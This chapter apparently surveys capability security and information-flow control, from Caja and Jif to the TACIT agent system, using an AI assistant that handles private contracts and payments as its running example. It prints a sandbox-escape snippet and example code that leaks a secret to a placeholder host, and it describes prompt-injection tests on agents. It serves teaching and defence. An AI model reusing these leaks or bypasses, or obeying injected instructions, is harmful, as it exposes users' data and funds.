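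Google used Caja in Google Sites and in Apps Script, its tool for automating documents. The bug hunter Michał Bentkowski found three ways to escape Caja and run hostile scripts on Google's pages, and described them for Securitum. Caja's security also depended on details outside the language itself, and a later hole came from its handling of HTML. Caja renamed forbidden HTML elements, such as `<title>` to `<caja-v-title>`. Browsers treat the contents of some elements as plain text, but after the renaming they treated the same contents as markup, which Caja had not filtered. Reid (2019), in *Caja Security Advisory 2019-06-06*, called this "a complete breach of the Caja DOM sandbox", the part that guards the page's contents.

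Google archived Caja on 31 January 2021, saying that nobody had kept it up to date with web security research and that it had several reported vulnerabilities. Software that still included Caja remained exposed. Jupyter Notebook, a programming tool popular with scientists, for example, used an outdated copy to sanitize untrusted notebooks. According to Averlon's *CVE-2021-32798*, a publicly known bypass let a malicious notebook run code when a victim opened it.

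*Google Caja*, a retrospective by one of Caja's designers, describes JavaScript's standard `Object.freeze` function as a result of the project. It traces Caja's continuation through Secure ECMAScript (SES) to Hardened JavaScript, with funding from the company Agoric. Hardened JavaScript needs much less code rewriting than Caja did. A program calls `lockdown()` once to freeze the built-in objects, then runs untrusted code in compartments. Each compartment has its own global variables and starts with only the frozen built-ins and whatever its creator adds, so it has no access to files or the network by default. Agoric uses Hardened JavaScript to run smart contracts, and the cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask uses it to run third-party extensions.

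Freezing can break existing code. Libraries that modify built-in objects must do so before the lockdown. Programs that modify nothing shared can also fail, because JavaScript doesn't allow assignment to a property that an object inherits as read-only. For example, `settings.toString = ...` can fail if `settings` inherits `toString` from a frozen object. Hardened JavaScript works around the most common cases of this problem.

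SES has also had flaws that let code escape. Code in a compartment must not use `import(...)` to load modules from the surrounding program. SES searched the source text for that expression but ignored `import` after a dot, since `x.import()` is an ordinary method call. An attacker could get past this search with `{...import(name)}`, where the three dots are JavaScript's syntax for copying properties. The maintainers fixed this in 2023 (CVE-2023-39532). Fixes also have to reach every copy of SES. According to a January 2019 thread in Google Groups' *Google Caja Discuss*, Agoric and Salesforce were not carrying their fixes back to the original.

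### Narrowing a credential sent over a network

A language can protect references only on machines that run it faithfully. Between machines, E represents an object by a long random number and a fingerprint that identifies the object's host. Anyone who learns the number can use the object, so E sends the number only over encrypted connections.

Attenuation is awkward in this setting because it matters where the forwarder runs. If it runs on Ana's machine, every request must pass through that machine. If it runs on the machine that hosts the target, a network failure may block her message to switch it off. Miller suggests a dead man's switch, which disables the forwarder when its host loses contact with the owner.

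Macaroons, which researchers at Google introduced in 2014, need no forwarder. A macaroon is a credential to which any holder can add restrictions, called caveats, without contacting the service that issued it. The method uses HMAC, a function that computes a short code from a secret key and a message. The code is easy to check with the key and infeasible to forge without it. Suppose Ana's bank has a secret key K and issues her a macaroon with the identifier `id` and the code s₀. Ana's program adds two caveats:

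s₀ = HMAC(K, id)  
s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "payee = the courier")  
s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "amount ≤ €50")

It passes on `id`, the two caveats and s₂, but not s₀ or s₁. The bank, which knows K, repeats the calculation, compares the result with s₂ and checks that the payment satisfies both caveats. The recipient can add a third caveat by using s₂ as the next key. To remove the €50 limit, it would need s₁, which it cannot work out from s₂.

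A basic macaroon is still a string, so an agent can leak it like any other access token. If it does, the caveats limit the damage to €50 for the courier, and an expiry time is also sensible. A single-use caveat requires the bank to record which macaroons it has accepted.

### Fifty euros, once

Suppose Ana asks her assistant to book a courier for up to €50, and enters the courier's account number herself. A trusted program holds `account`, which can pay anyone, and makes the assistant a weaker capability:

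```
def makeSinglePayment(account, payee, limit):
    used := false
    return object with
        pay(cents):
            if used: fail
            if cents is not a whole number from 1 to limit: fail
            used := true
            account.transfer(payee, cents)

permit := makeSinglePayment(account, courier, 5000)
```

The assistant can call `permit.pay(3200)` to pay €32. It cannot use the permit to follow the stranger's message and send €900 to an account abroad, because `pay` has no payee field and 90,000 cents exceeds the limit. If the assistant passes the permit to a separate booking agent, both hold the same object with the same `used` flag, so they can make only one payment between them. The assistant could also wrap the permit in another object that rejects payments over €40. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) suggests adding an expiry date to such use-once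 capabilities, and describes wrappers that record each delegation so an owner can trace misuse.

The program sets `used` before it contacts the bank. If it did so afterwards, a second call could arrive while the first was still in progress, and both would succeed. However, if a crash occurs during the transfer, the permit is used up, but the courier may not have received the money. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) presents a system for running agents that records the intended action and reserves its limited authority before making the call. After a crash, the system marks the outcome as unknown rather than automatically repeating the payment.

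The permit leaves an attacker some influence. The stranger's text could make the assistant overpay the courier, up to the limit, or pay for an unwanted booking and leave nothing for the real one. An assistant that has read Ben's contract could also leak about 12 bits of it to the courier through its choice among the 5,000 possible amounts. A free-text payment reference would let it leak far more, so `pay` has no such field.

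Like the reply capability for Ben's thread, the permit does not control what its holder does with text the holder is allowed to read. Zhang's system adds a separate check on where labelled data may go, but Zhang does not claim that it stops a trusted recipient from forwarding what it has received.

### Tracking capabilities in types

A programming language can narrow this gap if code handles secret text without releasing it as ordinary data. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) built a system called TACIT on this principle and described it in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, later published as *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities*. The agent writes short programs in Scala 3 instead of calling tools directly. Before a program runs, the compiler works out which capabilities each piece of code can use and records them in that code's type. The type of a function that writes to file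 `f` includes `f`, while pure functions have no capabilities in their types.

TACIT wraps secret text in a type called `Classified`. The agent can process the contents only by passing a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which accepts pure functions and wraps the result again:

```
secret.map(text => text.length)         # accepted
secret.map(text => file.write(text))    # rejected by the compiler
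```

The compiler also stops a program from keeping a capability outside the block of code it was granted for, so a file reference cannot escape as it did from the forwarder. Agent code may not use type casts or other features that would hide a capability from the compiler.

Pure functions cannot summarize a contract, so TACIT adds a second, trusted language model that runs locally and has no tools. This model takes wrapped text and returns a wrapped answer. When the agent prints the result, Ana sees the summary on her screen, but the agent's own model receives only `Classified(****)`. An instruction hidden in the contract could still distort the summary.

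Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a directory of secrets. They paired 12 legitimate tasks with 10 prompt injections, and added 11 requests in which the user directly asked for secrets or posed as someone entitled to them. The table shows how often the agent's output contained no secrets and how often the agent completed the legitimate tasks.

| Model | Secrets | No leak: 120 injection trials | No leak: 11 malicious requests | Tasks completed |
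|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | wrapped | 100% | 100% | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | plain text | 100% | 81.8% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | wrapped | 100% | 100% | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | plain text | 97.5% | 27.3% | 88.3% |

Even without the wrapper, the models leaked the secrets in only three of 240 injection trials, so those trials provide little evidence of its value. The malicious requests provide better evidence, because ten of 22 succeeded against plain text and none succeeded against wrapped text. The stronger argument for TACIT is that its design does not depend on how well a model resists persuasion.

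A second test used AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do banking, office, messaging and travel tasks while reading planted instructions. Across 963 attack trials for each of two models, the benchmark counted one successful attack, in which the agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review that recommended another. The test included no unprotected runs, so it does not show how many attacks the types stopped. It compared TACIT with CaMeL, a system that tracks the origin of data while an agent's program runs. The two completed similar shares of tasks in some areas and very different shares in others. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 53% of office tasks and CaMeL 81%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64% of travel tasks and CaMeL 1%.

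Writing typed programs did not make agents much less capable. On simulated customer service, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls. On a set of real software repairs, MiniMax M2.5's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7%. At most 8% of the customer-service programs had to be retried because the compiler rejected them. *What's in the Box* (2025) found that the checking takes little time, under 15% of total compilation time for Scala's standard library.

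TACIT's guarantees do not cover leaks through timing or any outside program the agent is allowed to start. The core type system has machine-checked proofs, but the full safe subset of Scala does not yet. Odersky and colleagues consider Scala 3 the only production-ready language with this kind of tracking. *LACUNA* (2026), which describes another agent system built on Scala 3, argues that its design could work in any statically typed language that tracks effects or capabilities, provided that a running program can recompile code.

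Ana's assistant also has to answer Ben's questions, so some trusted function must unwrap text about the contract and send it to him. `Classified` records that text is secret, but not whose secret it is. If Ana's payroll and the contract are both wrapped in `Classified`, a function that may send `Classified` text to Ben will send him either one.

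## Deciding who owns a label: the decentralized label model and Jif

A label that keeps Ana's payroll from Ben but lets him see the contract has to specify whose secret it protects and who may relax the protection. In the military model, a security officer assigns the labels, and a program that lowers one must be trusted by everyone whose data it touches. *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control* (Myers and Liskov, 1997) removed this central authority. In its decentralized label model, each party attaches a policy to its own data, and code acting for that party can weaken only that policy.

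### Owners and readers

A policy has an owner, who is the principal it protects, and a list of readers the owner allows to see the data. A label is a set of policies, and a principal can read the data only if every policy permits it. Ana might label her payroll {Ana: Carla} so that her accountant, Carla, can read it, and Ben might label the contract {Ben: Ana}. The empty label {} marks public data.

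Myers and Liskov, in *Protecting Privacy Using the Decentralized Label Model*, count an owner as a reader only if the policy lists that owner as one. They also mention an alternative in which owners can always read what they own. Later accounts of Jif, the programming language built on the model, use this alternative, as do the examples here. Ana and Carla can therefore read the payroll, and Ben and Ana can read the contract. A program may send data over a channel only if everyone who can read from the channel is allowed to read the data, so it can email Ben the contract but not the payroll.

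The join of two labels is the union of their policies. Suppose the assistant writes a summary that draws on Ana's project schedule, which she shares with Ben and Carla, and on Ben's contract:

{Ana: Ben, Carla} ⊕ {Ben: Ana} = {Ana: Ben, Carla; Ben: Ana}

Only the people whom both policies allow can read the summary. The table shows who can read it at first and after either owner relaxes a policy.

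| Label on the summary | Ana allows | Ben allows | Can read |
|---|---|---|---|
| {Ana: Ben, Carla; Ben: Ana} | Ana, Ben, Carla | Ana, Ben | Ana, Ben |
| {Ben: Ana}, if Ana removes her policy | everyone | Ana, Ben | Ana, Ben |
| {Ana: Ben, Carla; Ben: Ana, Carla}, if Ben adds Carla | Ana, Ben, Carla | Ana, Ben, Carla | Ana, Ben, Carla |

Ana cannot show Carla the summary, however much she relaxes her own policy, because Ben has not consented. But removing her policy lets Ben publish the summary alone, which he could not do before.

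This is why the model keeps a separate list of readers for each owner. If the label listed only Ana and Ben as owners and Ana and Ben as readers, then after Ana withdrew her restrictions, nobody could tell which readers Ben had allowed.

### Acting for others

Principals include groups and roles as well as people. If p acts for q, then p has all of q's powers. Members of a group act for the group, and a manager may act for each of the staff. Creating this relationship requires only q's authority, not an administrator's approval, because only q gives anything up. In the basic model, delegation is all or nothing, so if Ana lets her assistant act for her, the assistant can release all the data she owns. Myers and Liskov suggest splitting the relation so that a principal can delegate reading without delegating release.

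The acts-for relation enters into the ordering of labels. A policy J covers a policy I if two conditions hold:

- J's owner is I's owner or acts for I's owner.
- J allows no reader that I does not allow, where anyone who acts for a reader also counts as a reader.

Data may flow from label L₁ to label L₂, written L₁ → L₂, if each policy in L₁ is covered by some policy in L₂. Removing a reader or adding a policy is therefore safe.

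The rule requires a single new policy to be at least as strict as the old one because later delegations can weaken the combined effect of several policies. Suppose a program wants to replace {Ana: Ben} with {Ana: Ben, Carla; Ana: Ben, Dan}. Only Ana and Ben satisfy both new policies at first, but Carla and Dan might later hire the same secretary and let her act for each of them. She would then satisfy both policies, although the original label did not allow her to read the data. A compiler checks labels before these delegations are known, so the rule forbids the change. Myers and Liskov proved that their rule allows all relabelings that remain safe whatever delegations follow, and only those.

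Declassification uses the same ordering. Let L_A be a label with one policy, naming no readers, for each principal whose authority the running code holds. The code may change L₁ to L₂ if

L₁ → L₂ ⊕ L_A.

When the code runs with Ana's authority, L_A is {Ana: }. The code may change the summary's label to {Ben: Ana}, because {Ana: } covers the removed policy and Ben's policy remains. It may not change the label to {Ben: Ana, Carla}, because nothing would cover Ben's original policy. The new policy lets Carla read the summary, and {Ana: } belongs to Ana, who does not act for Ben.

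### Computing on data that nobody may read

The Bell-LaPadula model stops a program from reading data above its level, but the decentralized label model lets a program compute on data that none of its principals may read. It can allow this because the results carry the same policies as the data and cannot leave the system until the data's owners agree.

Myers and Liskov illustrate this with a tax program. A customer's figures have the label {Customer: Customer}, and the software firm's database of tax-saving methods has the label {Firm: Firm}. Intermediate results carry both policies, so neither party can read them. A small routine with the firm's authority removes the firm's policy from the finished form, and the customer receives it. The rest of the program runs with no authority, so a bug in it cannot release the database or the customer's figures.

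The same division suits Ana's assistant. The language model can work on the contract without any authority, while a short piece of ordinary code holds Ana's authority and decides what to release.

Each form still leaks some information about the tax firm's database, and a customer who submits many sets of figures can infer parts of the database from the answers. Myers and Liskov suggest that the firm charge more for each form than the leaked information is worth. The firm also has to trust the computer that runs the program, because a customer who controls that computer can take the whole database.

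### Guarantees about who influenced a value

Integrity policies have the same structure, with writers in place of readers. In Jif's later notation, Ana ← Ben means Ana guarantees that only she and Ben have influenced a value. The flow rule is reversed, since a value may always move to a place that demands a weaker guarantee.

Suppose the payment code requires an account number with the guarantee Ana ← Ana. A number that Ana typed meets the requirement. A number from Ben's email has at best Ana ← Ben, and the stranger's text has no guarantee from Ana, so the payment code rejects both. If Ana phones Ben and confirms his number, code with her authority can add the stronger guarantee. A guarantee from Carla would not meet the requirement unless Carla acts for Ana.

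Code can also corrupt a value without touching any other labelled data, as when a routine that is supposed to add two numbers returns something else. Myers and Liskov therefore give each function its own integrity label and combine it with the label of everything the function computes. By this rule, a language model that copies an account number out of Ana's notes counts as an influence on the result, even if the notes are entirely hers.

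### A short Jif program

Jif extends Java with labels and checks most of them when it compiles a program. This class, in the syntax of early versions, works out a price for Ben from Ana's private costs and a discount set in the contract:

```
class Quotes authority(Ana) {
  int{Ben: Ana} quote(int{Ana:} cost, int{Ben: Ana} discount)
      where authority(Ana)
  {
    int total = cost - discount;
    int{Ben: Ana} wrong = total;                          // rejected
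    int{Ben: Ana} price = declassify(total, {Ben: Ana});  // accepted
    return price;
  }
}
```

Each type has an ordinary part, `int`, and a label. The programmer gave `total` no label, so the compiler infers the join of its inputs, {Ana: ; Ben: Ana}, which only Ana can read. It rejects the assignment to `wrong` because the label {Ben: Ana} contains nothing that covers Ana's policy. (It also tracks flows through branches, which the next section explains.)

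The compiler accepts the `declassify` line because the class and the method both claim Ana's authority. Installing a class that claims her authority requires her permission. If the line instead made the price public by giving it the label {}, the compiler would reject it, because that would also remove Ben's policy.

The accepted line may still be a mistake. Ben knows his discount, so if he also knows the formula, he can work out Ana's costs from the price. Jif checks who authorized a release, but the programmer has to decide whether the release is wise.

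### What happened when people used Jif

In *Mostly-Static Decentralized Information Flow Control*, Myers (1999) expected label inference to keep annotating programs from being onerous. Askarov and Sabelfeld carried out an early test of Jif by implementing mental poker, a cryptographic protocol for playing cards online without a trusted dealer. Their program had 4,500 lines, compared with 500 and 800 for the largest earlier programs they knew of in languages of this kind. One graduate student spent about 60 hours writing a version in Java, 150 hours converting it to Jif and 80 hours making it run as separate processes, not counting the time to learn Jif. The conversion exposed possible leaks in the Java version, such as an error message that could reveal that a secret number was zero.

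The main class contained 14 declassifications. Two released data that was never secret, such as a public key stored with its private key. Eight released signatures, encrypted cards and similar protocol data, and one revealed whether drawing a card had succeeded. The last three revealed each player's key and shuffle after the game so that the opponent could check for cheating. Releasing these earlier would have revealed the player's hand, but Jif could not express when a release was allowed, so Askarov and Sabelfeld had to build a run-time flag, called a seal, to prevent early release.

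The program also had to copy an array element by element to change its label. Jif had no debugging tools, so the programmers debugged the Java version. The compiler relied on hand-written descriptions of Java's libraries. One description that came with Jif omitted the fact that a standard copying function writes to its destination, so the compiler accepted a program that used the function to copy a secret array into a public one.

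Civitas, an electronic voting system, has about 13,000 lines of code in an extension of Jif and 8,000 in plain Java. The policies in its labels can include conditions that determine when information may be released or must be erased. For example, each authority that counts votes must keep certain random bits secret until all the authorities have committed to theirs, and the system must erase a voter's secret credential after delivering it.

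In *SIF*, Chong, Vikram and Myers describe a framework for web applications written in Jif 3.0. They compare it with JPmail, an email client written in an earlier version of Jif. JPmail protected secrecy but not integrity, and it left the management of users to other software. SIF supports both secrecy and integrity policies, and its applications can add users, each with their own policies, while running.

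One of their two test applications handles messages that need approval. Suppose Sue writes to Tom, and reviewers Rita and Raj must approve the message first. It starts with this label:

{Sue: Tom, Rita, Raj; Rita: Raj; Raj: Rita}

Both reviewers can read the message, but their policies exclude Tom. Each reviewer removes their own policy when they approve the message. Once both have approved, only Sue's policy is left, so Tom can read it. No part of the program can skip a reviewer without that reviewer's authority. An agent's outgoing mail could go through the same procedure.

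The second application is a shared calendar, and both applications use the same library to manage users. Chong and colleagues counted the lines with label annotations and the places where the code deliberately lowered secrecy or raised integrity.

| Component | Lines of code | Lines with labels | Downgrading annotations | Distinct downgrades |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reviewed messages | 1,325 | 277 | 76 | 14 |
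| Calendar | 1,779 | 443 | 73 | 17 |
| User library | 925 | 283 | 31 | 8 |

About a quarter of the lines had labels even with inference, which is more annotation than Myers's thesis suggests. The annotations outnumber the distinct downgrades because releasing a data structure means releasing each of its fields. Of the 39 downgrades, 26 moved data to or from places that the developers had deliberately closed to unauthorized code, mostly the database. Another 12 were part of the application's purpose, such as adding a guest to an event. Only one resulted from the compiler's imprecision. A reviewer can find out what these 4,000 lines can release by examining the 39 downgrades instead of reading all of the code.

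The programmers were developers of Jif, and they still had to revise the declared labels of some methods several times as they discovered flows they had not considered. SIF also slowed the calendar, which handled at most 1,503 requests per second, against 2,010 for a similar program in plain Java.

SIF assumes that programmers may make mistakes but are not malicious. A hostile programmer could misuse declassification or leak data through channels that Jif does not track. Code that an agent writes after reading a stranger's message may be malicious, so it should run without any principal's authority.

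### Ownership as a logical formula

In 2011, Deian Stefan, Alejandro Russo and colleagues proposed a simpler format called disjunction category labels, which has no separate lists of owners and readers. The secrecy part of a label is a formula made of principals' names, "and" (∧) and "or" (∨). Ana's schedule becomes Ana ∨ Ben ∨ Carla, and the contract becomes Ana ∨ Ben. Combining data joins the formulas with "and":

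(Ana ∨ Ben ∨ Carla) ∧ (Ana ∨ Ben) = Ana ∨ Ben

Data may flow from a label with formula S₁ to one with formula S₂ if S₂ logically implies S₁. The summary, labelled "Ana or Ben", may go to a channel labelled "Ben", because "Ben" implies "Ana or Ben", but not to one labelled "Carla". Each label has a second formula for integrity, and there the source's formula must imply the destination's. Authority is also a formula, so the system no longer needs a record of who acts for whom. For example, "Ana and Ben" is stronger than "Ana" because "Ana and Ben" implies "Ana".

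Code with authority P may declassify from S₁ to S₂ if P ∧ S₂ implies S₁. In the example, "Ana" implies "Ana or Ben", so code with Ana's authority can release the summary to Carla, or to anyone, without asking Ben. Under {Ben: Ana}, by contrast, Ana could read the contract but only Ben could release it. The formula "Ana or Ben" lets either of them do both. The stricter formula Ana ∧ Ben would restore Ben's veto, but neither could read the summary until the other agreed to release it.

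A designer can recover the distinction by creating a principal for Ana's screen whose authority no code holds, and labelling the contract Ben ∨ AnaScreen. Ana can then read the contract, but her assistant cannot pass it on. Haav and Laud's *Typing Computationally Secure Information Flow in Jif* explains that later versions of the language also let programmers combine principals and policies with "and" and "or", but that Jif's labels still have owners.

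### When an agent needs owned labels

Two levels each of secrecy and trust are enough when everyone outside is equally untrusted and one person decides every release. For example, a coding agent that has to keep its user's keys off the internet and strangers' text out of its commands only needs to label data as secret or public and as trusted or untrusted. Chong and colleagues similarly argue that marking input to web applications as tainted or untainted can catch some common attacks, but cannot express the requirements of several users who distrust each other.

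Ana's assistant now needs more than two levels, because the payroll and the contract are both confidential but have different audiences. Categories of the kind Denning used, one for payroll and one for Ben's business, would keep the two apart without owners as long as Ana decides on every release. Ownership is worth the extra complexity when a release needs somebody else's consent, as it does if Ana and Ben share an assistant, or if a hosted agent combines the records of several customers.

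In those cases the owners must also trust whoever runs the system. On Ana's own computer, the label {Ben: Ana} is a promise from Ana to Ben, and she could remove it by changing the software. The label still prevents her assistant from forwarding the contract to Carla in response to an injected instruction or a careless request. Somebody also has to write Ben's policy, because email arrives without labels. A cautious default would make the sender the owner and the recipients the readers. The assistant would then need Ben's approval to send anything derived from his message to anyone else.

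## Checking before or during execution: static and dynamic enforcement

Jif's compiler enforces information-flow rules statically, rejecting a leaking program before it runs. Dynamic enforcement uses a run-time monitor that attaches labels to values and stops the program before a value goes somewhere its label forbids. The two approaches differ most in how they handle Denning's implicit flows, in which information escapes without being copied.

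Suppose Ana's assistant writes small programs, and `penalty` is true if Ben's contract contains a penalty clause:

```
fetch("http://site.example/" + penalty)            # explicit flow

if penalty then fetch("http://site.example/a")     # implicit flow
else fetch("http://site.example/b")
```

In the second case, the site's owner learns the same fact by seeing which page the program requests. A loop that tests one bit at a time could send the whole contract this way.

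Implicit flows can occur without an `if` statement. Smith's *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* gives a Java program that uses a secret bit to index into an array of length one. For one value of the bit, the access raises an exception and the program skips the next line. For the other value, the next line runs and records the bit in a public variable.

### The program-counter label

A static checker can catch implicit flows with a program-counter label, written pc. This label covers whatever an observer could learn from the fact that execution has reached a given line. It starts at the lowest level and rises inside a branch that depends on a secret. With L(x) for the label of a variable x, and L(e) for the join of the labels of all variables in an expression e, the rules are:

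- *Assignment:* accept `x := e` only if L(e) ⊕ pc → L(x).
- *Branching:* for `if e then c else c′`, check both c and c′ with the pc raised to pc ⊕ L(e), then restore the old pc.

Volpano, Smith and Irvine (1996), in *A Sound Type System for Secure Flow Analysis*, expressed the same idea as types. A variable of type τ var holds information labelled τ or lower. A command has type τ cmd if it assigns only to variables labelled τ or higher:

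e : τ var and e′ : τ  ⟹  (e := e′) : τ cmd  
e : τ, c : τ cmd and c′ : τ cmd  ⟹  (if e then c else c′) : τ cmd

All the parts must agree on τ, but the checker allows two conversions. A public expression may count as secret, and a command that writes only to secret variables may count as one that writes to public variables or higher. In `if x = 1 then y := 1 else y := 0`, either conversion makes the types agree when x is public and y is secret. If x is secret and y is public, neither conversion helps, and the checker rejects the program.

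Volpano and his co-authors proved that this analysis, which Denning had justified only informally, ensures a form of noninterference. If a program passes the check, any two runs that start with the same values in all public variables and finish successfully also end with the same values in those variables.

The proof uses counterparts of the two Bell-LaPadula rules. An expression typed as public reads only public variables, so it has the same value in both runs. A branch that depends on a secret writes only to secret variables, so the public memory is the same whichever branch runs. *A Correctness Proof for the Volpano/Smith Security Typing System* (Snelting and Wasserrab, 2008) later gave a machine-checked proof for a simple language without threads.

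The theorem covers only runs that finish, and this exemption is larger than it looks. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues (2008), in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, give this example:

```
for i := 0 to max
    output i publicly
    if i = secret then loop forever
```

The last number the program outputs is the secret. Jif and two similar tools accept the program because the branch that depends on the secret makes no assignments. Researchers had often said that ignoring termination leaks at most one bit per run, but that holds only if the program outputs nothing before it ends. Askarov and colleagues also proved that programs satisfying this kind of noninterference cannot leak a secret faster than by brute-force counting, which takes time exponential in the secret's length. That protects a 128-bit key, but a four-digit PIN can be leaked in at most 10,000 outputs.

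Static checking also rejects some harmless programs, such as `if secret = 0 then public := 1 else public := 1`. Better analysis can reduce these errors but not eliminate them. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) notes that neither static nor dynamic methods can detect violations of noninterference precisely. Any method must therefore miss some leaks, block some safe programs or change what programs do.

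### Why a simple monitor leaks

Languages such as JavaScript are hard to check in advance, because programs can build new code from text while they run. An obvious run-time rule is to mark a variable as secret whenever the program assigns to it inside a secret branch. In the following program, which Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, use to show the flaw, x is secret, and y and z start as public:

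```
y := true
z := true
if x then y := false
if y then z := false
```

| After this line | x is false | x is true |
|---|---|---|
| `z := true` | y = true, public; z = true, public | y = true, public; z = true, public |
| `if x then y := false` | y = true, public | y = false, secret |
| `if y then z := false` | z = false, public | z = true, public |

In both runs, z ends up equal to x and still has a public label. The error arises when x is false, because the program skips the assignment to y and the monitor leaves y public, even though y's unchanged value reveals x. A static checker avoids this error because it examines `y := false` whether or not that line would run.

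In *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis*, Austin and Flanagan (2009) proposed a dynamic check for such cases, now called no-sensitive-upgrade. The monitor stops the program before it assigns to a public variable while the pc is secret. Here it stops the program at `y := false` when x is true, and lets it finish with z = false when x is false. Someone who can tell whether the program finished still learns x, so this guarantee, like the static one, doesn't cover leaks through termination.

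The rule also stops programs that leak nothing:

```
y := true
if x then y := false
y := true
output y publicly
```

The output is always true, but the monitor stops the program whenever x is true. Ana's task could therefore work on one contract and fail halfway through on another.

### Four ways to stop fewer programs

**Permissive upgrade** adds a third label, "partially leaked", for a value that is marked as secret in this run but might be public in another. In the four-line example with z, when x is true, y becomes false and partially leaked. The program continues until `if y`, where the monitor stops it because branching on such a value could spread the leak. The harmless program above now finishes, since its last assignment replaces the partially leaked value with a constant. Austin and Flanagan proved that every run that finishes under no-sensitive-upgrade also finishes under permissive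 upgrade.

Programmers can prevent more stoppages by marking y as secret just before the test, whatever its current label. The monitor can also identify where these marks are needed as the program runs. Austin and Flanagan suggest first releasing a web application in a learning version, which gives users no guarantee, and enforcing the rules once new marks become rare.

In *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution*, Devriese and Piessens run the whole program once for each security level. The public run, which produces the public outputs, receives default values in place of secret inputs. The secret run receives the real inputs but produces only secret outputs. If the default for x is false, the public result of the four-line program is always z = false.

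One of their examples is a script in a web-based email client that adds the text of the user's message to the address of an image. Under their method, the script still requests the image, but the address contains an undefined value instead of the message. Programs that were already secure, under a definition that also counts leaks through termination, behave as before on runs that finish. Other programs change silently, so Ana might get poor search results without knowing that the public run had not received the contract.

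This method also prevents leaks through termination and timing, as long as a lower run never has to wait for a higher one. It requires extra computation, roughly in proportion to the number of levels if the runs take turns. Parallel runs use more memory instead, and some programs finished sooner because their runs could wait for the network at the same time. For an agent, each extra level would mean another set of model calls.

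A faceted value holds a private and a public version side by side, so the program needs to duplicate work only where the two differ. When x is true, its value is ⟨true | false⟩, with the private version first. Then y becomes ⟨false | true⟩ and z becomes ⟨true | false⟩, and a public observer sees false. According to *Faceted Secure Multi Execution*, by Schmitz, Algehed and colleagues, facets were meant to optimize running the program once per level, but they give a weaker guarantee about termination. Both versions belong to the same run, so an endless loop in the private computation can also block public output.

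**Floating labels.** LIO, a library for the functional language Haskell, gives the running computation a single current label. Reading a secret raises this label to the join of its old value and the secret's label. Before any visible action, LIO checks that the current label may flow to the destination. In simplified form:

```
text <- unlabel contract           -- current label is now Confidential
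fetch "http://weather.example"     -- refused
```

LIO blocks the request even though the address contains nothing from the contract, because the decision to send it might depend on what the program has read. In the four-line program, reading x makes the current label secret. If x is true, LIO blocks `y := false`, and if x is false, it blocks `z := false`.

The current label behaves much like Biba's low-water mark and has the same drawback. *Securing functional programs with floating-label information-flow control* (Buiras, 2016) describes a remedy, `toLabeled`, which runs a block of code and then restores the earlier label. But if the block never finishes, the code after it never runs, and an observer may notice. A concurrent version of LIO closes this gap by running such blocks in separate threads. Other threads must raise their own labels before they can find out whether a block has finished.

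LIO originally kept the label of each variable fixed. In *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems*, Buiras, Stefan and Russo (2014) warn that simply letting these labels change opens a high-bandwidth covert channel, and they present a safe way to change them.

The table compares what each method does with the four-line program.

| Method | x is false | x is true | Can termination leak secrets? |
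|---|---|---|---|
| Static type system | rejected in advance | rejected in advance | yes, in accepted programs |
| Simple monitor | z = false, public | z = true, public | yes, and z reveals x anyway |
| No-sensitive-upgrade | z = false, public | stops at `y := false` | yes |
| Permissive upgrade | z = false, public | stops at `if y` | yes |
| One run per level | public sees false | public sees false | no, with suitable scheduling |
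| Faceted values | public sees false | public sees false | yes |
| LIO | refuses `z := false` | refuses `y := false` | yes with `toLabeled`; no in the concurrent version |

### What implicit flows amount to in real code

Whether this effort is worthwhile depends on how often implicit flows matter in practice. *Implicit Flows* (King, Hicks and colleagues, 2008) examined six security routines written in ordinary Java. Three handled logins over SSH, a protocol for remote access, and three performed cryptographic operations (RSA, MD5 and DES). The researchers marked secret data, such as keys, and ran JLift, an extension of Jif that analyses whole Java programs. They then checked by hand whether the program path behind each alarm could occur.

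JLift raised 887 alarms. Of the 870 for implicit flows, 725 were false and 145 identified true leaks. All 17 alarms for explicit flows were correct. A tool that tracked only explicit flows would have raised no false alarms but would have missed 145 of the 162 true leaks, or 89%.

Most of the false alarms involved exceptions. Once a program has branched on a secret, any later line that might crash could reveal which branch it took, and the checker treats almost every line of Java as one that might crash. Five kinds of run-time exception, such as using a null pointer or going beyond the end of an array, caused 757 alarms, 706 of them false. Ordinary branches caused only 46, 14 of them false.

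Jif programmers have to work around the same problem. In the Civitas voting system's code, King and colleagues found 568 empty handlers for unexpected exceptions. In 429 of them, the programmers named the exception `imposs` because they believed it could not happen.

Not all of the 145 true implicit leaks were vulnerabilities. Most were technical violations of noninterference, such as an output buffer whose size depended on the length of the data to be encrypted. Some login routines revealed whether a username was valid, but only after the user had given the right password. The researchers did not try to rank the leaks by severity.

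In *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript*, Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues (2019) started instead from known security problems. They ran 56 vulnerable programs under a monitor to find which kinds of flow it had to track to detect each problem. They divided implicit flows into observable ones, where the program writes to a variable because a sensitive branch ran, and hidden ones, where a variable stays unchanged because the branch did not run, as y does in the four-line program.

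| Programs | Number | Tracking needed to detect the known problems |
|---|---|---|
| Server modules that may run an attacker's text as code | 19 | explicit flows |
| Server modules that an attacker's text can slow to a halt | 20 | explicit flows |
| Server modules that expose old memory contents | 7 | explicit flows |
| Browser scripts that identify visitors or detect their history | 10 | observable implicit flows in some cases |

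Only five programs contained hidden flows, and tracking those flows revealed no further problems. When the monitor tracked observable implicit flows in the server modules, every additional leak it reported was a false alarm. On average, no-sensitive-upgrade would have stopped programs at 5.46 times as many places as permissive upgrade, and most stops were unnecessary even under permissive upgrade.

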